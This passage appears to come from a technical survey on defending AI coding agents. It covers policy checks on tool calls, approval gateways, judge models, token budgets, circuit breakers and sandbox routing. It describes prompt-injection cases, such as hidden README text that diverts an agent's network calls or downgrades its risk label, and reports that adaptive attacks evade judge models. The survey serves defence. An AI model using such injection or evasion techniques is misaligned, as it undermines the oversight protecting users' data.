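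*NOMOS* (2026) turns written policies into checks on tool calls and tests them on AgentDojo, a benchmark that gives agents ordinary tasks with injected instructions in the data they read. In the banking tasks, attacks succeeded 46.5% of the time against an undefended agent using one model and 44.1% with another. With the checks in place, none of the benchmark's attacks ran. However, injected text could still divert payments to payees the user already had, which the benchmark did not count as a success. In a travel task, an agent emailed the user's passport and card numbers to an address the user had named in the request, because the written policy did not forbid it. A policy that restricts recipients therefore also needs to restrict what the agent may send them.

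### Deterministic authorisation before the call

A deterministic policy check always returns the same result for the same call and policy, and it uses no model that an attacker could manipulate. *Before the Tool Call* (Uchibeke, 2026) presents the Open Agent Passport, a specification for running such a check before each tool call. The passport is a signed credential that lists an agent's capabilities and limits. Each type of operation has a separate policy pack, which contains a schema for the required fields and a list of conditions under which the call is refused.

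The check proceeds as follows:

1. Deny the call if the passport is not active.
2. Deny it if the passport does not list the capability.
3. Deny it if no policy pack covers the capability.
4. Deny it if the agent's level of identity verification is too low.
5. Deny it if any refusal condition is true, such as an amount above the limit.
6. Refer it to a person if the passport requires approval.
7. Otherwise, allow it.

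For the upgrade, the passport could list web requests as a capability and the registry as the only permitted destination. The call to compat-check.example would then fail at step 5. If the policy service is unavailable, the system refuses the call. APort, the company behind the reference version, has not yet implemented step 6.

Uchibeke found that APort's cloud service took a median of 53 milliseconds per decision over 1,000 requests, excluding network latency. A local version took 174 milliseconds because it started a new Python process for each check.

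The main security test was a public contest in which people tried to talk an AI banking agent into making unauthorised transfers. The contest produced 4,437 policy decisions in 1,151 sessions. In the easiest tier, the policy permitted almost any transfer, and 588 of 788 attempts (74.6%) succeeded. In the hardest tier, none of 879 attempts succeeded and a $5,000 prize went unclaimed.

This comparison is weaker evidence than it appears. The paper describes the hardest tier as having "zero capabilities" and a $0 limit. Under that policy, any working policy engine would refuse every transfer, including legitimate ones. According to a later passage, the tier allowed transfers to listed recipients within set limits. That would make the result more impressive, but the paper does not report whether any legitimate transfer went through. Participants also chose their own tiers, and Uchibeke founded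 the company that sells the system. The contest does show that the engine still applied its rules even though participants often persuaded the model.

Testing whether a defended agent is still useful requires legitimate tasks as well as attacks. *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) reports such a test of an agent system called ELBA, using the model Opus 4.7. The researchers simulated the worst case by making the part of the agent that read injected text follow it directly. With policies in force, the system resisted all 735 injections, compared with 425 without the policies. However, it completed only 351 of the 735 tasks, about a third fewer than the 523 it completed without policies.

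A deterministic check can also consistently apply the wrong rule. *ToolGuardian* (2026) recommends testing whether each rule takes effect, altering rules to see whether the tests detect the change, and using scenarios written by people who did not write the policy.

The Open Agent Passport also evaluates each call separately, so it can miss a harmful combination of permitted calls, such as the file read and DNS change in the *AGATE* example. A stateful policy tracks earlier calls and can forbid outside requests once the agent has read a secret. *Sapien* (2026), a stateful policy engine, is tested by checking whether its policy permits any sequence of calls that reaches an attacker's goal. The attacker is assumed to control the agent already, so the result depends on the policy rather than on how well the model resists persuasion.

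### Drafts that wait for approval

Some calls should run only if a person approves the details. A draft-then-approve gateway stores the proposed action, shows it to a reviewer, and carries it out after approval. *OpenPort Protocol* (Zhu, Wang and colleagues, 2026) specifies a gateway that handles every request to change data this way unless an operator has allowed automatic execution for a limited time.

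Suppose the agent has finished the upgrade and wants to push its patch to a shared repository. It first asks the gateway for a preflight, a summary of what the push would change. The gateway returns the summary with a digest, a short value that changes if the underlying data change:

h = H(C(t, x, I(t, x)))

Here t is the tool, x the arguments and I(t, x) the expected impact. C writes all three in canonical JSON, so that differences in spacing or field order do not change the digest that H computes. If the agent later submits a different patch with the old digest, the digests do not match and the gateway does not execute the patch automatically. Canonical JSON does not resolve paths inside the arguments, so the gateway must resolve them before computing the digest.

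A colleague might change the shared branch while the draft waits for approval. An optional part of the protocol records a digest of the branch's state and refuses the push if that state has changed. The protocol also lets the agent retry if the connection fails just after the push. The agent can repeat the request with the same identifying key, and the gateway returns the earlier result instead of pushing again. The agent's credentials do not allow it to approve its own drafts.

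Zhu and colleagues tested whether their software follows the specification but not whether it stops attacks. Version 0.1.0 passed 20 unit tests, and 80 malformed requests caused no server errors. The tests did not yet cover repeated requests, the check for changed state or the completeness of the audit record. The paper reports no attack success rates and no trials with human reviewers.

The reviewer is a weak point because people tire and attackers can send many requests. *Treating the Model as an Untrusted Component* (2026) hypothesises that human approval helps only when it follows a deterministic check, and that reviewers become less effective when sent too many calls. It also proposes a fixed budget of approval requests to limit spamming. For the upgrade, the developer might review the final patch and any new package name but not every file read.

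### A second model as judge

A fixed rule cannot anticipate every unsuitable call, so some designs have a second model judge whether a call fits the task. Ge (2026), in *Governance Architecture for Autonomous Agent Systems*, tested this as one layer of a proposed Layered Governance Architecture. Each judge model received a task description and a tool call, and answered "ALLOW" or "BLOCK" with a one-sentence reason.

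The test set contained 1,081 synthetic calls. Of these, 504 were harmless, 457 resulted from prompt injection or poisoned documents, and 120 came from malicious plugins. GPT-4o-mini wrote the calls in Chinese and translated them into English. Ge, the paper's only author, checked the labels on a random tenth of the calls.

Five models served as judges, four running locally and GPT-4o-mini in the cloud. The table gives each result for the Chinese version first, then for the English. The false-positive rate is the share of harmless calls that the judge blocked, excluding 40 harmless plugin calls that Ge assessed separately.

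| Judge | Injected or poisoned calls blocked | False positives | Malicious plugin calls blocked |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3.5-4B | 95.8% / 94.3% | 27.5% / 29.2% | 86.7% / 83.3% |
| Llama-3.1-8B | 98.0% / 97.8% | 37.5% / 37.7% | 99.2% / 80.8% |
| Qwen3.5-9B | 96.5% / 95.0% | 34.1% / 23.7% | 77.5% / 77.5% |
| Qwen2.5-14B | 98.2% / 98.5% | 9.7% / 20.1% | 77.5% / 88.3% |
| GPT-4o-mini | 93.0% / 95.4% | 3.2% / 12.3% | 75.0% / 94.2% |

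The judges intercepted between 93.0% and 98.5% of the injected or poisoned calls, but their false-positive rates ranged from 3.2% to 37.7%. Malicious plugins were harder to detect because they perform the requested task but also do something harmful, such as sending a copy of a file elsewhere. Llama blocked 99.2% of malicious Chinese plugin calls, but that figure is misleading because it also blocked 87.5% of the harmless ones. The median delay per call ranged from about half a second to just over two seconds.

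These conditions favour the judge, because the attacker did not know about it or adapt to it. When Ge wrote 30 new samples designed to evade detection, GPT-4o-mini blocked 50% of them, and two of the local judges blocked 63%. Thirty samples are too few for a precise estimate, but the result is consistent with earlier work cited in *Only What You've Signed up For* (2026), in which adaptive attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the defences tested, including model-based filters.

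GPT-4o-mini also judged samples it had written. Ge argues that this did not inflate its interception rate much, because an unrelated model blocked a similar or larger share. But GPT-4o-mini may have recognised its own harmless calls, which would understate its false-positive rate. The judges were also small models, and the GPT-4o-mini version dates from July 2024, so a current large model might do better.

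### Why most blocks can be false alarms

Just over half of the calls in Ge's test set were malicious. In ordinary use, nearly all calls are harmless, and even a low false-positive rate then produces many more false alarms than real catches. The share of blocks that are correct is

I × p / (I × p + F × (1 − p)),

where I is the interception rate, F the false-positive rate and p the share of calls that are attacks.

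If 1% of 10,000 calls are attacks, there are 100 attacks and 9,900 harmless calls. In its Chinese results, GPT-4o-mini blocks 93.0% of attacks and 3.2% of harmless calls. At those rates it would block 93 attacks and about 317 harmless calls, so about 23% of its 410 blocks would be correct. Qwen2.5-14B, which blocks 98.2% of attacks and 9.7% of harmless calls, would block about 98 attacks and 960 harmless calls, so about 9% of its blocks would be correct. It would catch about five more attacks than GPT-4o-mini but block over 600 more harmless calls.

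Ge at one point credits the 22.7% figure to the best local judge. In the paper's table, however, that figure belongs to GPT-4o-mini, the cloud judge, and the figure for the best single local judge is 9.3%. An organisation that cannot send data to a cloud service should therefore plan with 9.3%. On the English samples, the figures fall to 7.3% for GPT-4o-mini and 4.7% for Qwen2.5-14B.

The 1% attack rate is an assumption and could easily be too high. If one call in 1,000 were an attack, fewer than 3% of GPT-4o-mini's blocks would be correct even with the Chinese results.

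False alarms also accumulate within a job. If the upgrade takes 40 harmless calls and a judge checking each one has an independent 3.2% chance of wrongly blocking it, the chance that the upgrade is interrupted at least once is 1 − 0.968⁴⁰, or about 73%.

A second judge can reduce false positives by reviewing only the calls that the first judge blocks. Ge calculated the combined result for Qwen3.5-9B and GPT-4o-mini from their separate answers. On the Chinese samples, the false positive rate fell to 1.9% and the interception rate fell to 91.9%. At a 1% attack rate, about a third of the blocks would then be correct. The router can reduce false positives further by sending only risky calls to a judge. Calls that are still blocked should go to a person or a safer environment where possible, because automatically ending the job would waste a great deal of legitimate work.

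### Where each resource limit applies

A permitted call can still fill the disk or run up a large bill. The new library's tests might start thousands of processes, or the agent might keep repairing and rerunning the same failing test. Neither case requires an attacker, which is why Podala Narasimha (2026), in *Containing the Autonomous Operator*, considers runaway loops the most likely harm in practice. The paper recommends budgets for tool calls, changes, spending and model tokens (the units of text, often parts of words, by which model services charge). It reports no measurements of how well these budgets work.

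Each limit belongs at a point that the resource cannot avoid. The example values below would suit a small project.

| Resource | Where the limit applies | Example for the upgrade |
|---|---|---|
| Processors | Kernel control group | 2 |
| Memory | Kernel control group | 4 GB |
| Processes | Kernel control group | 500 |
| Disk space | File-system quota or fixed-size volume | 5 GB |
| Elapsed time | Timer in the supervisor | 30 minutes |
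| Model tokens | Model proxy | 600,000 |
| Money | Model proxy, and gateway for paid tools | $5 |
| Tool calls | Gateway | 100 |
| Changes per object | Gateway | 3 pushes to one branch |

A control group is a Linux kernel feature that sets shared limits for a group of processes. New processes join the group of the process that started them, so the tests cannot escape the limit by starting more programs. If the group uses too much processor time, the kernel slows it down. If it runs out of memory, the kernel normally kills one or more of its processes. Control groups do not limit disk space, so it needs a separate quota.

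The model proxy, the part of the supervisor that forwards requests to the model, can count tokens and spending. The kernel cannot, because both depend on the content of a request to an outside service. The gateway counts tool calls and changes, but it misses the installer's changes to files inside the sandbox. A mutation budget, which limits the number of changes to one object, therefore works best for objects outside the sandbox, such as a shared branch or a running service.

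A rate limit caps how fast an agent can make requests, but not how many it can make overall, so it needs a separate limit on the total. The reference version of OpenPort accepts up to 240 requests a minute for each combination of credential and network address. At that rate, an agent could make 14,400 requests in an hour. OpenPort applies the limit before it creates a draft, which prevents a runaway agent from flooding the reviewer's queue.

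Token use grows faster than the number of calls, because the runtime normally resends the whole context to the model on each turn. If each of 20 turns adds 2,000 tokens, the last request contains 40,000 tokens, but all 20 together contain 2,000 × (1 + 2 + ... + 20), or 420,000. Some services charge less for text they have recently processed, but an attacker can still exploit this growth, since one very long tool result can add to the cost of every later turn.

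*Persistent Billable State* (2026) examines attacks that exploit such growth to run up the victim's bill. Its defences limit tokens per turn and per session and detect sudden growth in the context. The strictest setting permits 8,000 tokens in a turn and 20,000 in a session, while the most relaxed permits 100,000 and 200,000. Under the growth assumed above, the strictest session limit would end the upgrade after four turns and the most relaxed after 13, so designers need to measure ordinary jobs before choosing a limit.

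### One budget for parent and child agents

An agent may delegate parts of its work to child agents, which run in parallel. If each child receives a copy of the parent's limit, the combined limit grows with every child. A parent with 600,000 tokens, two children and one retry could use 2.4 million tokens without any agent exceeding its own limit.

The children therefore have to draw on the parent's budget. *Retrieval-Conditioned Topology Selection with Provable Budget Conservation for Multi-Agent Code Generation* (2026) expresses the rule for each resource in this way:

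c_A + ΣB_child ≤ B_A

B_A is the agent's budget, c_A is what the agent itself uses, and ΣB_child is the sum of its children's budgets. If every agent in the tree obeys this rule and stays within its own budget, the tree's total use cannot exceed the top agent's budget. Retries count against the same budget.

For the upgrade, the parent starts with 600,000 tokens. It keeps 120,000 for its own work and assigns one child to read the release notes and another to repair the failing tests.

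| Step | Tokens left in the pool |
|---|---|
| Parent starts | 600,000 |
| Parent reserves 120,000 for itself | 480,000 |
| Release-notes agent receives 160,000 | 320,000 |
| Test-repair agent receives 240,000 | 80,000 |
| Test-repair agent fails after using 180,000 and returns 60,000 | 140,000 |
| Release-notes agent finishes after using 100,000 and returns 60,000 | 200,000 |
| A new test-repair agent receives 200,000 | 0 |

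The retry would ideally get 240,000 tokens again, but only 200,000 remain. Even if the new agent uses them all, the total is exactly 600,000 (120,000 + 180,000 + 100,000 + 200,000). If the retry had started before the release-notes agent finished, it could have received at most 140,000.

Parallel agents can also overdraw a shared token pool if they request tokens at the same moment. With 80,000 tokens left, two agents requesting 50,000 each could both check the balance before either amount is subtracted, and together take 100,000. To prevent this, the supervisor has to check the balance and subtract the amount in one indivisible step.

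The proxy also has to subtract the amount from the budget before the model call. *Fault-Tolerant Budget Conservation in Distributed Multi-Agent Delegation* (2026) notes that an earlier system, Agent Contracts, checks its budget between actions, so one expensive call can exceed the limit before its cost is known. The proxy can prevent this by reserving the highest possible cost and returning any unused amount after the call. If 10,000 tokens remain and the request contains 8,000, the proxy should limit the reply to 2,000. If a connection fails and it is unclear whether the service charged for the call, the proxy should keep the amount reserved until the charge is confirmed or ruled out.

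The runtime still needs this running balance when a credential includes a budget. In *AIP* (2026), a protocol for delegating authority between agents, a signed token can limit an agent to spending 50 cents on a task. The software that verifies the token does not add up what the agent has already spent, because the protocol leaves that to the runtime. *Bounded Agents* (2026) requires limits to stay the same or fall as one agent delegates to another. That rule alone would let several child agents each spend up to the parent's limit, so the infrastructure must also track their combined use.

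Budget code needs the same input checks as any other tool. *Concordat* (2026), a programming framework for agents, subtracts a child's allowance from its parent's. Version 0.0.3 accepted negative amounts, so a parent with 100 units could give a child −50 and end up with 150. The next version fixed this by requiring amounts to be finite and non-negative. *Token Budgets* (2026) catalogues 63 incidents in which agents overran their budgets and proposes using the programming language Rust to prevent such faults. The Rust compiler rejects a program that copies a budget or uses it again after giving it away.

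### Circuit breakers

A budget stops an agent when it has used its allowance, but a circuit breaker can stop it earlier if its behaviour suggests that further attempts will be useless or harmful. Podala Narasimha proposes three triggers: repeated failures to repair the same object, repeated policy denials, and a change that does not improve the problem it was meant to solve. The breaker then hands the work to a person.

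In the upgrade, the supervisor might stop the agent after three patches in a row leave the same test failing. The job may have used only a quarter of its tokens by then, but a developer can probably find the incompatibility faster than the agent would on a fourth attempt. Five refused connections to unknown addresses should also stop the job, because the agent may be following the README or the new library may contain hostile code.

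A breaker triggered by cost can act too late. The one in *Persistent Billable State* ends a session when spending passes a threshold (between 5 and 50 cents in its presets), but it cannot recover the cost of the turn that crossed the threshold. It works best when combined with reserving budget before each call.

The supervisor has to store the breaker's counters and count failures across retries and child agents, because otherwise an agent could reset its count by starting a new child. Only a person should be able to restart the job, after reading why it stopped. An attacker may still trigger the breaker deliberately, for example with hidden text that makes the agent request forbidden addresses. This delays the developer's upgrade but doesn't leak the password.

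## Routing each operation to an isolation level

After a call passes the checks, the router chooses an isolation level for it, so that only risky operations are delayed by strong isolation. Running every operation in a separate virtual machine would be safest, but it would delay hundreds of harmless file reads. A single shared container would run an unfamiliar library beside the developer's own code. The examples below use three levels, from weakest to strongest: a restricted process, a container and a virtual machine. The router also sets conditions, such as whether the sandbox has network access, whether a judge model reviews the call, and whether a person must approve it.

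### What the router needs to know

The kind of operation matters most, because a file read only returns text, while a command can do anything its environment permits. The code's origin also matters. The command "npm test" looks the same before and after the upgrade, but afterwards it runs a library that nobody on the project has read. To distinguish the two cases, the router needs the supervisor's own record that the job has installed a new package.

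An operation is reversible if discarding the sandbox undoes it. Deleting every file in the agent's copy of the repository is reversible, but uploading one of those files is not. Stronger isolation does not stop an upload that the sandbox allows, so irreversible operations need approval or a strict limit on the destination.

The router also needs a way to identify sensitive data. In *Toward an Agentic Infused Software Ecosystem*, Marron (2026) proposes that developers mark sensitive data types, such as taxpayer numbers, in each service's definition. The runtime can then work out, without relying on the agent, which workflows have access to them. Most repositories have no such marks, so the operator of a coding agent has to list the sensitive files.

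Finally, the router must check whether the session has read text that an outsider could have written, because that text may contain a prompt injection.

### Routing the dependency upgrade

The table applies this evidence to the upgrade. It assumes that the sensitive configuration file is not in the agent's copy of the repository.

| Operation | Main consideration | Before the session reads untrusted text | Afterwards |
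|---|---|---|---|
| Read a project file | Runs no code and changes nothing | Restricted process, no network | Same |
| Run the tests with the old library | The developer already runs this code | Container, no network | Virtual machine, no network, because the agent may have altered the tests |
| Install the new package | Unread code may run during installation | Virtual machine, registry access only | Same, but a person approves any new package name |
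| Run the tests with the new library | Runs unread code | Virtual machine, no network | Same |
| Open another connection | Nobody can recall data once sent | Listed host: allow through the supervisor. Other host: ask the developer | Listed host: allow after a judge's review. Other host: refuse |
| Return the patch | The developer may later run the changed files | Restricted process compares the files without running them, and the developer reviews the result | Same, with changes to build scripts highlighted |

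The last column reflects session escalation. If B(o) is the level that the table gives operation o in a new session, and F(o) is the minimum level the session has since reached for that kind of operation, the router assigns

L(o) = max(B(o), F(o)).

F(o) can rise during a session but not fall. Reading the README raises it to "virtual machine" for anything that runs code.

The agent will probably read the README within its first few turns, so most of the upgrade will follow the last column. Few READMEs contain text that could affect an agent, but the router cannot reliably detect the ones that do, so it escalates based on where the text came from. For a public repository, the operator could start every session in the escalated state. Separating the normal and escalated states is more useful for a private repository that only colleagues can edit, where a session may run for some time before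 it reads an outside web page.

Marron proposes a similar measure for private data. After an agent uses a service that returns sensitive data, the runtime can quarantine all of the agent's output. Marron describes the design but does not test how well it prevents leaks.

### Four rules that protect the router

An attacker who can influence the router does not have to break a strong sandbox, because they can have the operation sent to a weak one.

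The router should ignore the agent's own risk labels unless they raise the isolation level. Suppose the command tool has a "risk" field that the model fills in. The stranger's text in the README could instruct the agent to label its compatibility check "low", and a router that relied on the label would run the check in a container with network access. A label that raises the level is safe to accept, just as a repository's policy file is safe to apply if it only removes permissions.

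The same caution applies to skills, which are packages of instructions and sometimes code that extend an agent. In *A Contract-Centered Architecture for Scalable and Manageable Agentic Runtimes* (Liu, Liu and colleagues, 2026), a skill cannot choose where it runs, grant itself credentials or change the platform's isolation. The paper also cites a collection of 138,133 skill files from 20,556 repositories. Almost 99% of the files have a structured header, which shows that skill authors usually supply a name and description, but not that they declare everything the skill can do.

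Unknown operations should go to the strictest level. A router might have a rule that sends "npm install" to a virtual machine and a default that sends other commands to a container. If the agent writes a script that downloads and runs the same package, the script runs in a container. With a strict default, the script runs in a virtual machine without network access, and the download fails. The strict default will slow down some harmless commands until the operator adds rules for them.

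A second check can catch the router's mistakes. Google's managed Kubernetes service can run sandboxes under gVisor, which handles a program's system calls in a separate software kernel. According to Kubernetes' *Self-Hosted Sandboxes*, recent versions of the service refuse any sandbox whose description lacks the setting that admits it to gVisor machines, so a router that mistakenly requested an ordinary container would get an error.

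The router should never lower the isolation level during a session without approval from outside the agent's trust domain. Runtimes often replace old text in a long context with a summary. If the router checked only the current context, it might return to weaker isolation once the README was gone, even though the summary could still contain the stranger's instruction. A child agent could also carry the instruction into a new session, so it has to inherit its parent's level. A developer who wants weaker isolation again can approve a particular operation or start over with the original request and a clean copy of the repository.

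The router should also hold no credentials. It processes arguments that an attacker may have written, so a bug could give the attacker control of the router and any credentials it held, such as the registry token. A safer router returns only the name of a level, and a separate launcher creates the sandbox from a fixed set of templates. A compromised router could still choose the wrong template, but it could not create one with more access.

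The dispatcher in Kubernetes' documentation comes close to this. It serves a product in which Anthropic runs the agent loop and puts work in a queue, while the customer's own cluster runs the tool calls. The dispatcher collects each work item, assigns it a sandbox and runs no untrusted code. However, the dispatcher and every sandbox hold a key to the queue, and that key belongs to the customer's whole environment. Code that found the key could presumably collect other sessions' work unless Anthropic restricts how a sandbox may use it. The documentation's claim that a compromised sandbox can affect only one session is therefore plausible for the sandbox's files but may not hold for the queue.

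### Passing data between sandboxes

Splitting a job across sandboxes creates a new risk, because two harmless steps can combine private data with an open connection. Suppose the new library needs a different format for the configuration file. The supervisor gives the file to a conversion sandbox with no network. The agent then installs an extra package in an installation sandbox that can reach the registry but contains no private files. Each step is safe on its own, but if the agent copies the converted file into the installation sandbox, the package's code gains access to both the password and a connection.

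Liu and colleagues cite research showing that components that are harmless alone can cause harm in combination. Their design therefore authorises the whole path, including its data and effects, instead of approving each component separately. They have not yet tested the architecture in operation.

A simple version of this idea uses two labels, "private" and "untrusted". Every file that leaves a sandbox carries the labels of everything the sandbox has received. Sandboxes have no shared folders or direct connections, so the supervisor moves each file and can check its labels against the destination.

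| Transfer in the upgrade | Labels | Decision |
|---|---|---|
| New package to the test sandbox | Untrusted | Allow, because the test sandbox has no network |
| Converted configuration file to the installation sandbox | Private | Refuse |
| Test output to the agent loop | Untrusted, and private if the tests used the configuration file | Allow only without the private label |
| Patch to the developer | Untrusted | Allow for review |

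The agent loop needs this restriction because its context goes to the model service, and an operator may be willing to send source code there but not passwords.

Labels tend to spread, so after several steps nearly every file may count as both private and untrusted, including files that contain nothing private. A person then has to release individual files, so the operator should keep private files out of the job where possible.

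### Warm pools on Kubernetes

Starting a virtual machine for each test run would keep the developer waiting, so operators often maintain a warm pool of sandboxes that are already running. Agent Sandbox, an open-source project for Kubernetes, provides one. A program submits a claim based on a template, and the system assigns it a sandbox from the pool (Kubernetes, 2026).

The project also has a Sandbox Router, which Kubernetes' *Overview* describes as a web proxy that forwards requests to existing sandboxes, a different job from that of the router discussed here. A setting in the template determines the isolation level, and can select gVisor or Kata Containers, which runs each pod in a small virtual machine. A team using Agent Sandbox would therefore write its own router to decide which pool to claim from. Kubernetes' *Warm Pool Quickstart* supplies suitable templates, including a gVisor sandbox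 whose only outgoing traffic is address lookups, one with access to a private model, and one that uses Kata.

Starting a sandbox in advance makes it available sooner but does not strengthen its isolation. Red Hat (2026), which offers its own build of Agent Sandbox, treats warm pools of pre-started sandboxes and virtual-machine isolation as independent options, so a warm pool may contain only ordinary containers.

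Kubernetes' *Documentation* says a warm sandbox is available in milliseconds. The worked example in Kubernetes' *Kata-Isolated Per-Owner Agent Warm Pool on AKS*, which uses virtual machines on Microsoft's cloud, gives "a couple of seconds". Neither page reports measurements. Claiming 20 separate virtual machines at two seconds each would add 40 seconds to a job, so the router should reuse a machine within the job when the next operation has the same labels and network rules.

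Large services can also exhaust a pool. Kubernetes' *Performance Assessment* puts the sustained refill limit for one pool at about 70 to 85 sandboxes per second and recommends splitting loads above about 30 claims per second among several pools. A small pool can run out much sooner. When no virtual machine is available, the router has to make the job wait, because if it used a container instead, an attacker could weaken other users' isolation by claiming all the virtual machines.

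### Quotas and clean state between tenants

Tenants are the teams or customers that share a cluster. Each needs a limit on how many sandboxes it can hold, and Agent Sandbox can use Kubernetes' ordinary resource quotas for this. Tenants also share the server that processes claims. Kubernetes' *APF Insulation for the Agent Sandbox Controller* describes settings that reserve part of the server's capacity so that other tenants' requests and pool refills don't delay new claims. The default installation does not include these settings.

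The supervisor has to authenticate each tenant. In the Microsoft cloud example, every user gets a separate virtual machine, and the proxy uses labels in the web request to find it. Kubernetes warns that the label naming the user is not a security boundary, because anyone can write another person's name in it. The example also accepts requests without authentication, so anyone who finds its public address can send requests to the sandboxes. The project's Go client library cannot yet send the token that would fix this.

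The example blocks connections between different users' sandboxes. However, its network rule permits encrypted web connections to any host, so two sandboxes could still exchange data through an outside website. The page nevertheless describes the access as enough to call the model provider "and nothing else".

Each job needs a new sandbox to start from a clean state. Kubernetes contrasts this with Anthropic's basic self-hosting setup, in which long-lived workers process one session after another in the same working directory. A malicious test in one session could leave an altered script there for the next session to run. In the Agent Sandbox version, each pod serves one session, then the system deletes and replaces it.

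A warm sandbox starts before anyone knows which tenant will use it, so the template must not contain a tenant's files or credentials. The supervisor adds them after the sandbox is claimed. Storage that outlives the sandbox needs the same separation. In the dispatcher's documentation, each session has its own output directory, because results from different sessions would otherwise mix even though every pod is new.

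Some runtimes cannot switch levels this easily. OpenShell supports containers and virtual machines, but NVIDIA's *Sandbox Compute Drivers* states that each gateway accepts only one compute driver. A team that wants both a container driver and a virtual-machine driver would therefore need two gateways, with the router choosing between them. The page also places OpenShell's supervisor inside the sandbox, whereas Abdollahi and colleagues describe it in a separate environment. Operators should check which arrangement their version uses before relying on a trust boundary between the supervisor and the sandbox.

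### Containers for GPU work, virtual machines otherwise

Sometimes the hardware limits the choice of isolation. *Steerability via constraints* (Winninger, 2026) describes a setup for one developer's laptop that runs the agent in a virtual machine unless the agent and the developer both need the graphics processor (GPU). In that case it uses a container, because giving a virtual machine access to the GPU would be too cumbersome. Winninger regards the container as the weaker boundary and accepts that it would not contain an attack through the GPU driver.

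The container runs without administrator rights, has a read-only system and can start at most 200 processes. The virtual machine writes each session's changes to a separate disk layer over a fixed base image. Both send their network traffic through one proxy, which allows connections only to listed sites, including package registries, code-hosting sites and model services. Rules in the host's kernel also block access to the developer's private network.

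The agent can read the developer's repository but not write to it. It works on a copy, and the developer later fetches the changes and decides which to merge. For the upgrade, the developer would get the patch without giving the agent a credential for the main repository.

With this design, the developer should decide whether a job needs the GPU when starting it. If the router relied on the agent's claim, an injected instruction could obtain the weaker container simply by requesting a GPU. If the new library's tests need a GPU, the developer could run most of them in the virtual machine and the rest on a separate computer with nothing valuable on it.

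The single proxy makes the network rules easier to maintain, but it gives both runtimes the same list of sites. Tests that need no network could still reach a code-hosting site, where an attacker might have an account. The router would need to set separate network rules for each operation to prevent this. Winninger calls the system a prototype and recommends replacing its sandbox and network parts with OpenShell. The paper's experiment tested whether a small model could find backdoors in code, and Winninger did not test the system's isolation.

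### What routing saves and what mistakes cost

Routing can also reduce the time spent on judge models. Suppose a job makes 200 calls, 20 of them high-risk, and a judge takes one second per call, which is within the range Ge measured. Judging only the high-risk calls adds 20 seconds to the job, instead of the 200 seconds added by judging every call.

Checking fixed routing rules takes almost no time by comparison. Liu and colleagues cite a runtime whose rule checks took 0.021 milliseconds per request, or about four milliseconds for 200 calls. They treat this figure as a lower bound because it excludes work such as schema validation.

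Now suppose the router mistakes 5% of the high-risk calls for low-risk ones. On average, one of the 20 calls then skips the judge.

| Arrangement | Time spent judging | High-risk calls that skip the judge |
|---|---|---|
| Judge every call | 200 seconds | 0 |
| Judge high-risk calls, no routing errors | 20 seconds | 0 |
| Judge high-risk calls, 5% misrouted | 19 seconds | 1 on average |

Misrouting a high-risk call past the judge saves one more second but leaves the call unchecked. If 5% of high-risk calls are misrouted and errors are independent, about 64% of jobs with 20 high-risk calls will contain at least one unchecked call (1 − 0.95²⁰). Misrouting also nearly doubles the number of attacks that get through. A judge that stops 95% of attacks lets 5 in 100 through if it sees them all. If 5 of those 100 skip the judge, it misses about 4.75 of the other 95, so nearly 10 get through.

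Even this estimate assumes that errors are random. If the router always misclassifies one kind of command, an attacker who discovers this can use that command every time. The misclassified call skips the judge's review and may also run in a weaker sandbox, so one mistake can defeat two layers that should fail independently. Denying network access at every isolation level unless a rule specifically grants it would preserve some protection.

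Sending a harmless call to the judge is a much less serious mistake than letting a dangerous one skip it, since the check usually adds one second. If the router treated another 20 doubtful calls as high-risk, judging would take 40 seconds in total, still 160 seconds less than judging every call. The operator could also send a random tenth of the remaining 160 calls to the judge, which would add 16 seconds, and use any dangerous calls found to correct the routing rules.

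## Choosing and configuring the sandbox

The router picks an isolation level, and the operator has to build a sandbox that provides it. Sandboxes differ mainly in how much of the host's kernel the agent's code can still reach. A program uses system calls to request actions from the kernel, such as opening a file, starting another program or sending data. Linux has several hundred system calls, and a flaw in the code that handles any of them may let a program take control of the computer.

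### What each mechanism shares with the host

The lightest sandboxes restrict an ordinary process. Seccomp, a Linux feature, limits which system calls a process may make. It can stop a program from loading a driver, for example, but it can't distinguish one file from another, because the call passes the file's name as a memory address and the filter can't read the memory there. With Landlock, another Linux feature, a process gives the kernel a list of directories it may read or write, and the kernel applies the list to that process and every program it starts. Neither feature needs administrator rights, but with both, every permitted call still runs in the host's kernel.

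A container adds namespaces, the kernel feature that gives it a view of files, users, network devices and other processes separate from the host's. Podala Narasimha points out that the container still shares the host's kernel, so a single vulnerability there is enough for an escape.

gVisor, which puts a software kernel between the container and the host, has two parts. According to *Securing Operating Systems Through Fine-grained Kernel Access Limitation for IoT Systems* (2025), Sentry handles most system calls itself, and Gofer passes file requests to the host. The host's kernel still handles some calls, so the paper considers gVisor weaker than the small virtual machines of Kata Containers. *Shrinking the Kernel Attack Surface Through Static and Dynamic Syscall Limitation* (2025) agrees and adds that gVisor lacks some system calls, so it supports fewer programs than Docker, the best-known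 container system.

A compiler translates a WebAssembly program into a restricted set of instructions, and the program can reach only its own memory and the functions that the runtime provides. If the runtime provides no function for opening files, the program cannot open any. *SideKernel* (Prasakis, 2026) classes this as language-level isolation because the boundary lies inside the runtime. The runtime is an ordinary process on the host, so a flaw in it can expose the host's kernel.

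A full virtual machine has its own kernel and emulated devices, such as disks, displays and network cards. Each device adds code on the host that the agent can attack. A microVM keeps the separate kernel but has only a few devices. Firecracker, which Amazon uses for Lambda, runs microVMs. On Linux, part of the hypervisor runs in the host's kernel, so an agent in a microVM can still attack some host kernel code. A confidential virtual machine also protects the guest from the host, but it does not remove this code.

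### Speed, compatibility and GPU support

In *Sandlock*, Wang and Zheng (2026) compared their own process sandbox with Docker on one workstation. They also list start-up times for gVisor and Firecracker but did not test either. *Tracekit Box* (Ghosh, 2026) gives a slightly longer start-up time for Firecracker, in the low hundreds of milliseconds. The figures for gVisor's runtime overhead come from *Caging the Agents* (2026), which describes one healthcare deployment. The table combines these figures with general properties of each mechanism.

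| Mechanism | What must work correctly | Start-up | Running cost | Compatibility | GPU |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Seccomp and Landlock | Host kernel | About 6 ms in Sandlock | No measurable loss in a database test | Common build tools run if they can write temporary files | Through the host's driver |
| Container | Host kernel and container software | About 300 ms | Database ran at 76% of normal speed | Most Linux programs | Through the host's driver |
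| gVisor | gVisor and the host kernel code it uses | About 200 ms | 2–5 ms per new connection, 20–40% on sequential reads | Some system calls missing | Some NVIDIA GPUs, through the host's driver |
| WebAssembly | Its runtime and the host kernel | No comparable figure | No comparable figure | Only programs compiled for it | Limited |
| Firecracker | Hypervisor and a few devices | About 100 ms or more | Memory for a second kernel | Most Linux programs, on hardware that supports virtualisation | Normally none |
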